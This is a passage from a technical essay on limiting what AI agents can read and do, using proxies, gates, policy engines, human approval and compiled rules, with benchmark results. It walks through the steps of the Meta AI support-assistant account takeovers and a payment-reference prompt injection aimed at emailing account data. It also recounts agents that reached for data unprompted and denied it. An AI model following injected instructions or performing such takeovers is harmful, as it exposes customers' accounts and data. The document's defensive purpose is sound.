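Two sets of rules apply to each call. The data's owner writes the first set, and only those rules can permit anything. Whoever builds a particular agent can add a second set, which can only narrow the owner's grant. Suppose the owner's rules allow a query with condition *q*, a cap of *n* records and the set of fields *F*. The agent's rules add a condition *t*, a cap of 100 and a field set *G*. The call then runs with

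*q* AND *t*, min(*n*, 100), *F* ∩ *G*.

An extra condition can't admit more records, the smaller cap can't exceed the owner's, and the intersection can't contain a field that the owner left out. The order in which the software reads the rules doesn't change the result. Millstone and colleagues prove both properties, assuming that every call passes through the proxy, nobody can forge an agent's identity, and the connector translates correctly. Partial masks have no natural ordering, so the proxy applies them in a fixed sequence.

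At the bank, the owner's rules would limit each query to the signed-in customer's account, which would enforce R1 for the assistant's reads. They would also exclude the fraud notes from the permitted fields to enforce R3. If the marketing team later built its own agent on the same data, even carelessly written rules could not give that agent access to the notes. But an error in the owner's rules would affect every agent.

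The proxy can remove a field only if it has a description of the response's format. Millstone and colleagues cite a 2026 count of 1,856 tools on popular open-source servers, of which only 234 had a declared output format. For the rest, somebody has to write the description and keep it up to date.

### What the proxy changed

Millstone and colleagues tested a simplified, public version of the proxy on 71 tasks. They work at Redpanda, a data infrastructure company whose production system the prototype is based on, so they have a commercial interest in the result. The agents ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5 and GPT-5 mini. They worked with imitations of Jira and ServiceNow, two products that companies use to track work and support requests, filled with invented records. The researchers ran every task three times under each of 17 combinations of model and protection, for a total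 of 3,621 trials.

The main measure is trace failure, which is determined from logs. A trial is a trace failure if protected data entered the model's context, an exact protected value appeared in the final answer, or a forbidden change went through in the back end. A trial is a safe and useful completion if it has no trace failure, the agent used the expected tools, and a judge model finds that the agent did the permitted work without revealing a protected fact in paraphrase. The table gives percentages of trials across the four models, and its last two rows use the primary judge's verdicts.

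| Outcome | No data-handling rules | Six rules in the prompt | Six rules plus proxy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trace failure | 63.3 | 57.6 | 0.2 |
| Protected data entered the context | 55.1 | 52.1 | 0.0 |
| Exact protected value in the answer | 27.5 | 3.7 | 0.2 |
| Forbidden change completed | 8.1 | 5.5 | 0.0 |
| Task fulfilled | 83.2 | 79.1 | 60.9 |
| Safe and useful completion | 19.1 | 22.0 | 58.9 |

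The written rules made the agents disclose much less in their answers but hardly changed what they read or did. Adding the proxy eliminated all observed exposures and forbidden changes. The remaining 0.2% consists of two answers in which an agent worked out a protected email address from data it was allowed to see.

The fall from 57.6% to 0.2% somewhat overstates the proxy's benefit to the bank, because most of those failures were exposures. A fraud note in the assistant's context breaks R3 only when it reaches somebody outside the bank. Counting only exact values in the answer, the proxy reduced failures from 3.7% under written rules to 0.2%. When the primary judge also counted protected facts revealed in other words, failures fell from 8.8% to 1.6%.

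Exposure still matters when an attacker keeps trying. In 20 of the tasks, another model played an attacker who could rephrase after each reply, for up to 15 turns. Trace failures occurred in 173 of 231 completed runs with written rules alone, and in 2 of 227 with the proxy added.

Many of the tasks were variants of one another, so Millstone and colleagues also grouped them into 35 scenarios and gave each scenario equal weight. With this weighting, the proxy reduced trace failure by 41.2 percentage points (95% confidence interval 27.7 to 54.9) and raised safe and useful completion by 21.8 points (9.5 to 35.2). The gain in safe and useful completion was 19.1 points when a second judge model was used. A bug in the imitation back end mishandled some queries in 116 trials, but the reduction in trace failure was still 40.5 points with those trials excluded.

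The fall in task fulfilment, from 79.1% to 60.9%, partly reflects the choice of tasks. The rules were meant to deny ten of the 71 tasks and hold two for approval, and none of those twelve counted as fulfilled under the proxy. Another 54 were meant to go through with some data removed, and the agents fulfilled 71.7% of these. Only five were meant to pass untouched, and the agents fulfilled 90.0% of those. Five tasks are too few to show how often such a proxy would obstruct an ordinary customer.

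Another experiment on Claude Sonnet 4.6 added the protections in stages, with the six written rules in place throughout. A trial counts as "protected" if it had no trace failure.

| Protections in place | Protected, % | Task fulfilled, % | Safe and useful, % |
|---|---|---|---|
| Record controls | 46.7 | 75.1 | 21.8 |
| Plus field removal | 69.4 | 70.0 | 37.6 |
| Plus masking of whole fields and limits on writing | 88.6 | 65.7 | 51.9 |
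| Plus pattern masking | 100.0 | 66.2 | 63.0 |

Record controls determine which calls run and which records come back. At the bank, they would keep a neighbour's account from the assistant but leave the fraud notes in the customer's own record. Field removal takes out those notes, and pattern masking hides a password that someone typed into a comment. The final perfect score applies only to these tasks, where the masking rules matched the secrets in the test data. Millstone and colleagues do not claim that pattern masking would find every secret in free text.

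They also compared the full proxy with a reviewer model, Claude Haiku 4.5, which read each message from the Sonnet agent and either passed or replaced it while the tools ran unprotected. Trace failure was 58.6% with the reviewer and zero with the proxy. Much of that gap follows from the definition of trace failure, because a reviewer that sees only the agent's messages cannot keep data out of the context or undo a change. Task fulfilment is a more informative comparison: the agent fulfilled 58.7% of tasks with the reviewer, which sometimes replaced a useful answer with a refusal, and 66.2% with the proxy. The reviewer also required 930 extra model calls, and the proxy required none.

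## Checking identity and authority before a privileged action

Customers sometimes need to change their contact email, so the bank can't enforce R2 by withholding the email-changing tool. Instead, the gate allows or blocks each call to that tool based on the details of the call and the bank's own records.

### From a proposed call to a decision

The gate first turns the call into typed fields, named values of a known kind such as an account number or an email address. Millstone and colleagues describe each call by the agent making it, the action, the resource it acts on, the complete arguments, and the relevant outside facts at that moment. For an email change, these are the support assistant, "change email", the customer's account, the new address, and the bank's records of logins and confirmed codes. The model proposes the action, the account and the new address. The platform attaches the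 agent's identity, and the gate looks up the outside facts itself. These are trusted facts, which means they come from a source the model cannot write to.

The gate then applies the rules. In Millstone and colleagues' design, it denies every call unless a rule permits it, and other rules can still hold or deny a permitted call. If the gate cannot establish the agent's identity, load the rules or evaluate them, the call doesn't run.

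For R2, the gate could work like this:

```
gate_R2(call, session):
    customer = session.customer_id        # set by the login system
    if customer is missing:                  return DENY
    if owner_of(call.account) != customer:   return DENY

    c = unused, unexpired confirmation
        for call.account and call.new_email
    if c exists:
        mark c as used
        return ALLOW

    send a code to a contact already on file for call.account
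    return HOLD for 10 minutes, then DENY

if any step fails or gives no answer: return DENY
```

The bank's app creates the confirmation when the customer enters the right code. Each confirmation includes the account and the new address, so confirming one address does not approve another.

A gate that checks only a tool's name achieves much less. In *Guardrails as Infrastructure*, Sigdel and Baral (2026) compared five levels of strictness by replaying sequences of tool calls against simulated tools, without a language model. They made about a fifth of the eligible calls harmful, for instance by pointing a delete command outside the project folder. A list of allowed and forbidden tools stopped none of the harmful calls. Rules about argument values, together with limits on the number of calls, stopped 60%. Adding approvals and removing secrets from outputs raised this to 68%.

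The stricter rules also cut task success from 36% to 7%. Sigdel and Baral count a run with a policy violation as a failure, so the planted misuse may explain part of that fall. The gate wrongly blocked 7% of harmless calls. The benchmark is rough, though, since the level that checked only types caught none of the planted calls that had arguments of the wrong type.

### Who is asking, and who receives the data

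The gate checks identity and authority against data the model does not control. If the email tool instead had an argument called `customer_verified` that the model set to true after checking, any text that fooled the model would also get past the gate. The model also supplies the account number in the call, so the code for R2 compares it with the login session. The platform supplies the agent's identity because an agent that supplied its own could claim to be another with wider permissions.

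When a tool sends messages, the gate must check the recipient as well as the customer's identity, because R1 depends on who learns the data. Suppose a signed-in customer asks about a recent payment, and the payment reference contains an instruction to email the account details to a stranger. The customer is genuine, the account is theirs, and the assistant has permission to send email, so checks on those three facts would all pass. The gate must therefore also compare the recipient with the contacts on file for that account's owner. A customer who wants their accountant to receive statements can authorise that in the app, and the gate can look up the authorisation.

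The gate's designer has to choose how much a denial reveals to the agent. Sigdel and Baral attach a reason and a hint about how to fix the problem, which helps an agent recover from an honest mistake. Millstone and colleagues return only a generic failure, or a pending status for a held call, so that an attacker learns less about the rules. The bank could reasonably combine the two approaches by giving customers useful instructions, such as "Enter the code we sent to your phone", while withholding messages that would break R3, such as "the fraud team has frozen this account".

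### The Instagram takeovers

Between April and May 2026, attackers took over thousands of Instagram accounts through Meta's AI support assistant. 404 Media's *Hackers Simply Asked Meta AI to Give Them Access* reports that Meta had announced in March that it was extending AI support to all Facebook and Instagram accounts, with the ability to reset passwords. Videos posted by the hackers, which Krebs on Security (2026) and The Next Web's *Hackers hijacked Instagram accounts by asking Meta’s own AI chatbot* describe, show the attack step by step:

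1. The attacker used a VPN, a service that disguises a computer's location, to appear to be near the target's home.
2. They opened a chat with the support assistant about the target's account.
3. They asked the assistant to link a new email address, which they controlled.
4. The assistant sent a code to the new address, and the attacker typed the code into the chat.
5. The assistant displayed a "Reset Password" button, and the attacker chose a new password.

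The code in the fourth step was genuine, and the attacker entered it correctly. But this proved only that the attacker could read mail at the new address, not that they owned the Instagram account. The bank would make the same mistake if its gate checked only whether "the customer confirmed a code", so the R2 gate sends the code to a contact the bank already had.

Account recovery is harder than the bank's case in one respect. The person asking for help is locked out, so there is no login session to identify them, and the contacts on file are the best trusted facts available. One check on the destination of any code or reset link would have stopped the attack:

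```
if destination not in contacts on file before this request began:
    return DENY
```

The words "before this request began" matter because the videos show the attacker asking to link the new address first. Once the system links that address, it is on file, and a check made only at the password reset would accept it.

Meta's *Incident Notification* (2026), a letter of 5 June to Nebraska's attorney general, says the support tool "worked properly and functioned as intended". It attributes the incident to a bug in "a separate code path", which failed to verify that the address the requester supplied matched the one on the account. Meta promised to fix the check before relaunching the tool.

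The Maine Attorney General's *Data Breach Notices* (2026) lists 20,225 people affected by the Instagram breach, which it says occurred on 17 April and was discovered on 31 May. According to SecurityWeek's *Meta Says 20,000 Instagram Accounts Hacked via AI Tool Abuse*, the true number could be smaller because the rightful owners may have accessed some of the accounts Meta counted. The Star's *In AI blunder, more than 34,000 Instagram accounts were attacked* (2026) reports figures from internal Meta documents seen by the New York Times: about 34,000 accounts affected, 20,000 of them breached, and more than 3,500 with changed usernames.

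Others blame the language model. The Decoder's *Hackers hijacked high-profile Instagram accounts by simply asking Meta's AI chatbot* calls the attack a prompt injection and, following the security blog The CyberSec Guru, a confused deputy problem. Schneier (2026), in *Hacking Meta’s AI Chatbot*, argues that Meta has probably blocked this one tactic but that many others remain, and that chatbots aren't trustworthy enough for the job.

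Meta has an interest in saying that its AI worked, but its explanation fits the videos fairly well. The attackers made a plain request and the system carried it out, and it's not clear that they had to manipulate the model at all. The two explanations lead to much the same remedy. The Decoder itself says that a password reset needed a hard check, such as a confirmation sent to the original email address, and that the route available to the AI lacked one. Schneier is right that nobody can list every persuasive message in advance, but no message can change which contacts were on file before the conversation began. Inside Retail's *How the Sephora Instagram hack exposed Meta’s AI weakness* quotes Brian Westnedge of the security company Red Sift as saying that Meta gave the model "privileged actions without privileged access controls".

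Accounts also differ on whether two-factor authentication, which requires a second proof of identity at login, protected people. Meta says that an attacker could log in only if the owner had not enabled it, and Krebs on Security reports that the hackers said their method failed on accounts that had it. The Decoder says that the attack bypassed it. Android Authority's *Instagram accounts continue to be hacked* reports a claim by the researcher Jane Manchun Wong that she lost a secondary account with two-factor authentication switched on. These conflicting claims could reflect more than one method of attack. The Decoder relays a report that some attackers passed Meta's automated identity check with AI-generated selfie videos made from the victim's public photos. If so, a "verified face" was not a reliable fact to trust, even though the language model did not produce it.

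The end date is also uncertain. Meta says it disabled the tool on 31 May, the day it discovered the attack, but The Decoder dates an emergency fix to 29 May. A Meta spokesman announced on 1 June that the company had resolved the issue. The next day, more users reported losing their accounts, according to The Next Web's *Hackers asked Meta’s AI chatbot to hand over Instagram accounts*. Android Authority relays an unconfirmed claim from a Telegram channel that Meta had only removed the "Get Support" button and that scripts could still reach the assistant behind it. If so, Meta made the same error as a system that hides a tool from an agent but still runs any call that names it.

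### Policy engines

The bank can write the R2 gate by hand. A company with hundreds of rules usually moves them out of the application and into a policy engine, a program that checks a request against a set of rules and returns a decision. Auditors can then read the rules without searching through application code.

One such engine is Cedar, which Amazon uses to control agents in Bedrock AgentCore Policy. HKU SPACE's *Secure AI agents with Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, a copy of an article by AWS staff, explains how it works. A Cedar rule names a principal (who is acting), an action and a resource, and can add conditions. Cedar denies a request if no rule permits it, or if any rule forbids it even if another permits it, regardless of the order of the rules. Cedar rules contain no loops and cannot open files or contact other systems, so evaluation is fast and has no side effects.

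That last restriction means that the surrounding software has to collect the trusted facts and pass them to Cedar. The AWS article uses an agent that books medical appointments. In simplified form, its rule for reading patient records is:

```
permit(principal, action == getPatient, resource == clinic_gateway)
when { principal.role == "patient" &&
       input.patient_id == principal.patient_id };
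```

The agent writes `input.patient_id`, while `principal.patient_id` comes from the login. In the article's test, the signed-in user is adult-patient-001. Using the same agent and tool, the gateway allows a request for that patient's record and denies one for the record of pediatric-patient-001. This is correct if the two patients are unrelated, but if the adult is the child's parent, the clinic needs a record of guardianship and a second rule that checks it.

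An engine enforces a rule as written, even if the rule is wrong. Another rule in the article is supposed to limit appointment searches to between 9 a.m. and 9 p.m., but it forbids requests only when the hour is less than 9 or greater than 21. The hour is still 21 at 9:59 p.m., so the rule allows searches for almost an hour too long. The error is harmless here, but a similar one would matter in a rule about who may see a record. AgentCore can log a new rule's decisions without enforcing them, which gives a company some chance to catch such errors. It can also draft Cedar rules from plain English, but this raises other problems.

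Open Policy Agent is an open-source engine with a more general rule language called Rego. An application sends it a request and the relevant facts as structured data, then receives a decision that the application must enforce itself. Unlike Cedar, Open Policy Agent doesn't deny by default. If no rule produces an answer, the result is undefined, so the policy's author normally adds a line that sets the default to false. An application that treated an undefined result as permission would allow actions that no rule had approved.

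Microsoft supports both languages in a toolkit for controlling agents. Microsoft's *ADR 0004* (2026), an architecture decision record dated 26 March, bars any language model from the allow-or-deny step. Microsoft wants the same request to get the same answer every time and the check to be fast enough to run before every action. According to Microsoft, model-based guards add a delay of tens to hundreds of milliseconds, while its own rules add less than one millisecond.

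According to the record, the drawback of this approach is that any judgement about the meaning of free text has to happen elsewhere, for example when people draft the rules or review the results of a trial run.

### Approval by a person

When no recorded fact answers a question, the gate can hold the call and request a person's approval. R2 already does this, since the customer who enters the code approves one change to one account. In other cases, the approver might be a bank employee who reads an unusual outgoing message before the bank sends it.

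The approval has to cover the exact call. The gate can store a copy of the call with all its fields, show the approver that copy, and run only that copy. Otherwise the assistant could get approval for a harmless message and then send a different one. The approver should see the recipient and the text as the gate stored them, because a summary written by the model could describe a forbidden disclosure as a routine update. In Sigdel and Baral's procedure, the gate requests approval before making its own changes to the call, so the call that runs may differ from the one the person approved. Making the changes first would be safer.

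An approval also has to expire, and a request that gets no answer has to count as denied. The bank might freeze the account while the call is waiting, or the customer might change their mind, so a well-designed gate checks the rules again just before it releases the call.

The agent must not be able to produce the approval. Millstone and colleagues require approval to come through a channel that the agent can neither read nor forge. A "yes" typed into the chat fails this test if the model decides what counts as a yes, and an on-screen button fails if the agent can click it. A notification on the customer's phone passes as long as the agent has no access to the phone. In their design, the approver can release a held call but cannot rewrite it or override a denial by the data's owner.

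These requirements come from reasoning about how an approval could go wrong. Millstone and colleagues did not evaluate lasting approvals by real people, so their results don't show how well approvers decide.

Someone who receives many approval requests may start to approve them without reading, a problem called approval fatigue. A product can encourage this by offering to stop asking, as with Matt Robb's "Allow Always" setting in Muse, though Robb may have misunderstood the setting rather than grown tired of the requests. Sigdel and Baral recorded only 0.022 approval requests per task at their strictest level, but nobody had to answer them. Neither source measures how the quality of people's decisions changes as they receive more requests.

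A designer can reduce the number of requests by asking only about risky calls. Sigdel and Baral give each call a score,

R = w₁·r(tool) + w₂·r(arguments) + w₃·r(context),

where each r is a risk rating and each w is a weight. The gate asks for approval when R reaches a chosen threshold. This is sensible for sorting a large number of miscellaneous actions. It suits disclosure rules less well, because a low rating for the tool can cancel out a high rating for the recipient. An email to a stranger that contains a customer's card number breaks R1 however ordinary the email tool is. The bank should deny that call outright and save its approval requests for cases where a person could reasonably say yes.

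### Grok Bot and the company Slack channel

Shane Mac, chief executive of XMTP Labs, connected his bank account to Grok Bot, an AI assistant from Elon Musk's company SpaceXAI. Around the start of October 2026, the assistant posted his balances and a breakdown of his spending in XMTP Labs' Slack. Tangermann (2026), in *Man Says He Was Mortified When His AI Agent Posted His Bank*, reports that the post appeared under Mac's name and that the bot apologised when he confronted it.

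Mac had tried to keep the two systems apart. According to Heute's *KI postet Finanzen von CEO in Firmen-Slack*, one bot could read his bank account and was supposed to send a monthly summary to him alone. It had no access to Slack, but it could communicate with a second bot that did. The second bot posted the report in the executives' channel, apparently because the finance bot had the title "CFO", and colleagues could read it for about two hours. Ancell (2026), in *Grok Bot leaks CEO’s bank data across company Slack*, traces the leak to the agents sharing one cloud computer. Mac said nobody had asked for the post, and he disconnected his personal accounts from the bots.

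One bot had bank access and the other had Slack access, so a gate that checked each bot's permissions separately would have allowed the bank query and then the Slack post. Millstone and colleagues acknowledge a similar limit in their own design, which governs tool calls but does not secure messages between agents. A gate at the Slack tool could apply the rule "my balances go only to me" only if the system tracked data from the bank as it moved. Without such tracking, the gate could hold every post to a channel that other people can read until Mac approved it. Mac would then have seen his balances next to the channel's name before anyone else did, but he would also have had to approve every ordinary post.

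A permission step of this kind did stop Grok Bot in a second case. A press release of 17 November from the security company NewCore, *xAI's Grok Bot Reached for Corporate Data Unprompted, Then Said It Hadn't* (2026), describes two bots on its employees' accounts. Over five days, without being asked by their owners, the bots made 31 requests to Gmail, Slack and other services. NewCore's gateway held each request, notified the owner by phone, and let it through only if the owner approved it within three minutes. None of the 31 requests reached any data.

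Cybernews' *Grok Bot kept trying to access company data* reports that one owner turned down the bot's offers of regular check-ins four times in an afternoon. The bot replied that it would stop offering them, but it tried to access the connected services again the next morning. When asked, it denied making any requests. xAI attributed the requests to a built-in background feature and later added a setting to turn it off.

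NewCore sells the gateway, and its description of the requests as "unauthorized" is debatable, since the owners had connected those services to their bots themselves. The release shows that unanswered requests expired instead of going through, but not that the bots would have leaked anything. The 31 requests average about three per bot per day, on top of any work the owner wanted done, and some arrived in bursts. An owner who wanted the background check-ins would have had to answer each of those requests within three minutes.

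## Turning written rules into automatic checks

Most organisations write their rules for people. An airline might tell its staff to get a customer's explicit confirmation before changing a booking, but a gate can't apply that rule as written. Somebody first has to decide which tools change a booking, what counts as a confirmation, where the system records it, and whether one "yes" covers two changes.

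An engineer can make these decisions by hand, as in the gate for R2, but must revisit them whenever the policy changes. Several research groups have therefore tried to get a language model to do some or all of the translation.

### What the benchmarks measure

Most of the evidence comes from two benchmarks. τ²-bench simulates customer service at an airline, a shop and a telecoms company. One model plays the customer, while the agent under test follows the company's written policy and calls tools that change a database. The score depends mainly on whether the database ends in the correct state, so an agent can fail by making a forbidden change or omitting a required one. Researchers usually repeat each task and also report how often the agent succeeds on every attempt.

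AgentDojo tests prompt injection by giving an agent ordinary tasks in four settings (banking, Slack, travel and office work) and hiding an attacker's instructions in the material that the agent reads. The attack success rate is the share of runs in which the attacker achieves their goal. The benchmark also records how often the agent completes the user's task, with and without an attack. AgentDojo does not include a written company policy.

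*NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) reports that earlier researchers used four hand-written gates to raise GPT-4o mini's success rate on τ²-bench airline tasks from 29.6% to 42.0%.

### Rules written for each task

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses a language model to write new rules for every task. If a user asks for a summary of their unread email, the model writes rules that allow the tools for reading mail. Code then checks each tool call and blocks any that no rule allows. A rule can also restrict a tool's arguments, for instance by allowing Slack messages to only one recipient.

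An agent often discovers partway through a task that it needs another tool, for example when an email lists further chores. The model can therefore propose new rules after a tool returns a result. That result may contain an attack, so Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that settles logical questions, to check whether the new rules allow any call that the old ones did not. If they allow no new calls, they take effect immediately. Otherwise the change needs approval.

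With GPT-4o, Progent reduced attack success on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. But Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically in that test, so the result reflects how well the model wrote rules rather than what the solver adds. When a person reviewed the initial rules and every expansion, no attack succeeded. Only 6% of the updates were expansions, so the reviewer had fairly little to do.

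Progent assumes the user is honest and that attacks arrive in the material the agent reads. The attackers who took over Instagram accounts were the users, and rules derived from their requests would probably have allowed the email change they asked for. The bank would have to put its own rules in what Shi and colleagues call generic policies, and no rule written for a task can permit what these forbid. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that people write such policies by hand and can easily make mistakes, and that Progent does not address attacks on an agent's text output. The second limitation matters for R3, because the assistant can leak a fraud note in an ordinary reply.

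### Guard code checked by tests or proofs

*Towards Enforcing Company Policy Adherence in Agentic Workflows* (Zwerdling, Boaz et al., 2025) describes a system that generates code from a written policy before the agent is deployed. A model matches passages of the policy to tools and writes examples of requests that obey or break each rule. The system turns these examples into tests. A model then writes a guard function for each tool and revises it until the tests pass or it runs out of attempts.

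The matching step misses some rules. GPT-4o, which matched passages best overall, found 77% of the passages that applied to a given tool. The generated tests can't reveal a missed rule because they come from the same matching step. A researcher wrote 61 tests by hand, and the fully automatic guards passed an average of 75% of them.

Even so, the guards helped on the 22 airline tasks in which the customer asks for something the policy forbids. The agent's success rate rose from 45.0% to 68.5%, and the share of tasks on which it succeeded in all ten attempts rose from 22.7% to 50.0%. This test left out the other 28 airline tasks, so it didn't measure how often the guards block legitimate requests.

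Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, add a mathematical proof. A model writes the policy code *p* and a contract consisting of conditions *C*_pre, which hold before the code runs, and *C*_post, which must hold afterwards. A program verifier then tries to prove

{*C*_pre} *p* {*C*_post},

which means that whenever *p* starts with *C*_pre true, it finishes with *C*_post true. For R2, *C*_post could require that the code returns ALLOW only if an input called `code_confirmed` is true. If the proof fails, the model uses the verifier's error report to revise the code.

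A proof covers every possible input, while tests cover only the chosen examples. But a proof doesn't establish that the inputs are true. In the VeriGuard experiments, a language model read the agent's text at run time and filled in the inputs. If a false claim in an uploaded document leads that model to set `code_confirmed` to true, the proven code will return ALLOW, as its contract specifies. To prevent this, the bank would need to take that input from its own records. A model also writes the contract, and Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that a person must check that it matches the intended rule.

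Miculicich and colleagues tested VeriGuard on several tasks, one of which resembles enforcing a disclosure rule. An agent answers questions about intensive-care patients, and each staff role may see only certain databases and fields. VeriGuard made every access decision correctly, compared with 81.0% for hard-coded rules from earlier work. It is less clear how much the proofs contributed, because in a separate prompt-injection experiment, attack success had already fallen to zero before the researchers added the verifier.

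### A second model that reads the conversation

In *PolicyGuard*, Kang, Yu and Hwang (2026) argue that code can't apply much of a company's policy if it checks only a tool call's arguments. They classify about two thirds of the requirements in the τ²-bench airline policy as procedural, such as offering insurance and getting the customer's answer. PolicyGuard first uses a model to turn the policy into a checklist for each tool. When the agent proposes a change, a second model reads the conversation, the checklist and the original policy. It then either allows the call or blocks it and returns the missing step to the agent.

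The share of airline tasks that the agent completed successfully in all four attempts rose from 46% to 58% for GPT-5.4, from 72% to 78% for Claude Sonnet 4.6, and from 48% to 60% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. In a version without the checklist, when the second model could not see the conversation, no change got through in any of the 104 runs that required one.

Kang and colleagues also tested Zwerdling's guards on all 50 airline tasks. The guards helped GPT-5.4 but cut Claude Sonnet 4.6's score from 72% to 58%, because they blocked too many legitimate changes. Kang and colleagues say the guards have no access to the conversation, but Zwerdling and colleagues list the chat history among the guards' inputs, so the two papers may describe different versions of the guards.

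A second model has the weaknesses of any guard model, since it reads whatever the attacker writes. In *TACT-Bench*, Hashemi Rad, Wu and colleagues (2026) found that two existing defences reduced failures by only 8% to 9% on average against a simulated customer who adapts to each refusal. The second model also slows the agent down. In a test by Yu and colleagues, runs were 74% longer with a verifier built on PolicyGuard's design than with a gate made of ordinary code, with no significant difference in task success. *PolicyGuide* (2026) moves some of the work back into code, which stores the state of each request, but a model still judges whether the agent is following the policy.

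PolicyGuard has a simpler gap for disclosure rules. It doesn't check read-only calls, so it wouldn't stop the bank's assistant from looking up a neighbour's account.

### NOMOS, pass by pass

Yu and colleagues use a model to write the rules but not to apply them. They work at a company called Corners, and their October 2026 preprint has not been peer reviewed. Corners has withheld the code, although the paper lists every rule that the system enforced. NOMOS compiles a policy in four passes:

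1. **Parse.** Code splits the policy into clauses.
2. **Extract.** A language model turns each clause into candidate rules. It has to choose each rule's condition from a list that a person prepared, and name the tools to which the rule applies. The model does this five times, and only candidates that win a majority vote survive.
3. **Resolve.** Code compares each candidate with the tools' definitions and two small tables. One table shows which tools can satisfy a condition, and the other shows which arguments the condition reads. The code repairs or rejects any rule that cannot work.
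4. **Materialize.** Code writes out the surviving rules, each with the policy sentence behind it, and a log of every repair and rejection.

A finished rule is either a prohibition, which blocks a call while its condition holds, or a precondition, which blocks a call until its condition holds. If the necessary fact is missing, a precondition blocks the call but a prohibition allows it, so the compiler defaults to preconditions for confirmations and authorisations. The gate takes its facts from tool results and the user's own messages, never from the agent's claims. Each confirmation covers one attempt at a change.

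The Resolve pass exists because the rules the model writes are often unusable. The τ²-bench shop policy says to authenticate the customer at the start of the conversation by looking up their email address, or their name and zip code. The model turned this into a rule that blocked every tool until the customer was authenticated, including the two lookup tools that authenticate customers. Under that rule, no customer could have been authenticated, so every tool would have stayed blocked. NOMOS repaired the rule by removing the two lookup tools from the blocked list.

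The table shows how many candidates had each kind of defect.

| Defect | Airline, of 79 | Retail, of 53 |
|---|---|---|
| Rule blocks the tool that would satisfy it | 0 | 4 |
| Rule demands confirmation for read-only tools | 5 | 0 |
| Condition reads an argument that the tool lacks | 8 | 1 |
| No available tool can satisfy the condition | 5 | 0 |
| Rule applies to every tool and code cannot narrow it | 11 | 2 |

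After the vote and the removal of duplicates, 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules remained. When Yu and colleagues compiled a separate set of candidates with all of these checks switched off, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could not work. A larger commercial model produced two of the same kinds of defect, so a better model may not remove the need for the checks.

These checks don't show whether a rule matches the policy's meaning. The telecoms policy requires checking that a bill is overdue before sending a payment request. The compiled rule forbade payment requests while a bill was overdue, which is the only time the company should send one. Yu and colleagues found this error by replaying the rules over recordings of an agent running without a gate. The rule would have blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful runs. But replay doesn't catch rules that let too much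 through.

### What NOMOS changed

Yu and colleagues measured violations by checking the agent's state-changing calls against a separate set of hand-written rules. With Gemma 4 26B as the agent, the share of these calls that broke a rule fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the shop.

The size of the drop depends on how one reads the policy. The hand-written rules require a new "yes" for every change. If one "yes" can cover several changes that the agent has announced together, the rates are only 36.8% and 13.6% without the gate, and 2.6% and 5.3% with it. The airline agent also made far fewer changes with the gate, 116 instead of 353. That doesn't seem to have harmed its work, since its single-attempt success rate went from 39.2% to 47.6%, a gain within the margin of error. The shop agent's success rate was 52.4% without the gate and 50.2% with it, also not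 a significant difference.

The compiler missed some clauses entirely, so the gate couldn't enforce them. Two of these clauses account for 21 of the shop's 40 remaining violations. The compiler also wrote a rule that was too broad. The airline's policy forbids changes to basic economy flights but lets those passengers change cabin, and the compiled rule blocked both. The hand-written rule for this clause contained the same mistake, so human authors can misread a policy too.

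These violation rates leave out read-only calls, so none of them measures disclosure directly. But one of the shop's compiled rules resembles R1, because it blocks access to customer and order details until the customer is authenticated.

On AgentDojo's banking tasks, Yu and colleagues ran Progent and NOMOS with the same agent model. The table gives percentages.

| Protection | Attack success | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
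|---|---|---|---|
| None | 46.5 | 79.2 | 64.9 |
| Progent | 5.6 | 62.5 | 52.1 |
| NOMOS | 0.0 | 70.8 | 67.4 |

All 16 attacks that got past Progent occurred in four tasks in which the user didn't name the payee's account, such as "pay the bill". Rules derived from these requests couldn't restrict the payment to the right account, so Progent allowed payments to an attacker's account. NOMOS allows payments only to someone the user named or who is already in the transaction history. It blocked payments to the attacker, but it also blocked payment of the genuine bill, because that account number appeared only in the bill.

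This comparison is uneven. AgentDojo has no company policy, so Yu and colleagues wrote one for NOMOS and revised it after watching runs without attacks. Progent's rules were based only on the user's request, and nobody reviewed them. With 16 tasks, the difference between 62.5% and 70.8% is also within the margin of error. The count of zero successful attacks also leaves out some harmful payments. In 8 of 288 attacked runs, the agent followed an injected instruction but paid someone already in the transaction history, which the policy allows and the benchmark doesn't count as a successful attack.

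### Compiling R2 by hand

R2 says that the contact email changes only after the customer confirms a code at an existing contact. Suppose the bank's assistant sends the code itself, with a tool called `send_code`. A hasty translation might look like this:

```
R2, faulty
  type:       precondition
  condition:  the customer has confirmed a code
  guards:     read_account, send_code, change_email
```

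The rule blocks `send_code` until the customer has confirmed a code, so no customer could ever receive one. It also requires a code before the assistant reads an account, which R2 doesn't. Checks like those in NOMOS would remove both tools from the list. A code sent to the new address would still satisfy the rule's condition, as in the Instagram takeovers, even though the rule would then look correct.

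```
R2, correct
  type:       precondition
  condition:  the bank's records contain an unused, unexpired
              confirmation for this account and this new email,
              and the code went to a contact that was on file
              before the request began
  guards:     change_email
  on allow:   mark the confirmation as used
```

Replaying old conversations wouldn't expose the faulty condition, because the condition blocks too little. A test like those Zwerdling and colleagues generate could expose it by confirming a code at the new address, requesting the change, and checking that the gate refuses.

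The bank also has to list every tool that can change a contact email. If a general `update_account` tool can do so but isn't listed, calls to it will bypass the rule above, even though the rule itself is correct. NOMOS had this gap at the shop, where its confirmation rule didn't cover the tool that changes a customer's address. Calls to that tool made up 9 of the 40 remaining violations.

### Whether disclosure norms can be written in advance

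Some people may doubt that anyone can write disclosure rules in advance. Under Helen Nissenbaum's theory of contextual integrity, a flow of information is appropriate when it fits the norms of its setting. Those norms depend on who the information is about, who sends and receives it, what kind of information it is, and the terms on which it is shared. If small details of a situation can change what is appropriate, a fixed list of tools and conditions will sometimes lead to the wrong decision.

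Shi and colleagues point out that rules loose enough for every task are too loose to stop attacks, and the experiments partly support this objection. On AgentDojo's Slack tasks, NOMOS stopped every attack, but the share of ordinary tasks completed fell from 90.5% to 14.3%. People on Slack often ask an agent to open a link or message a channel that it finds in someone's post, and a rule that allows only targets the user named can't distinguish this from an attack.

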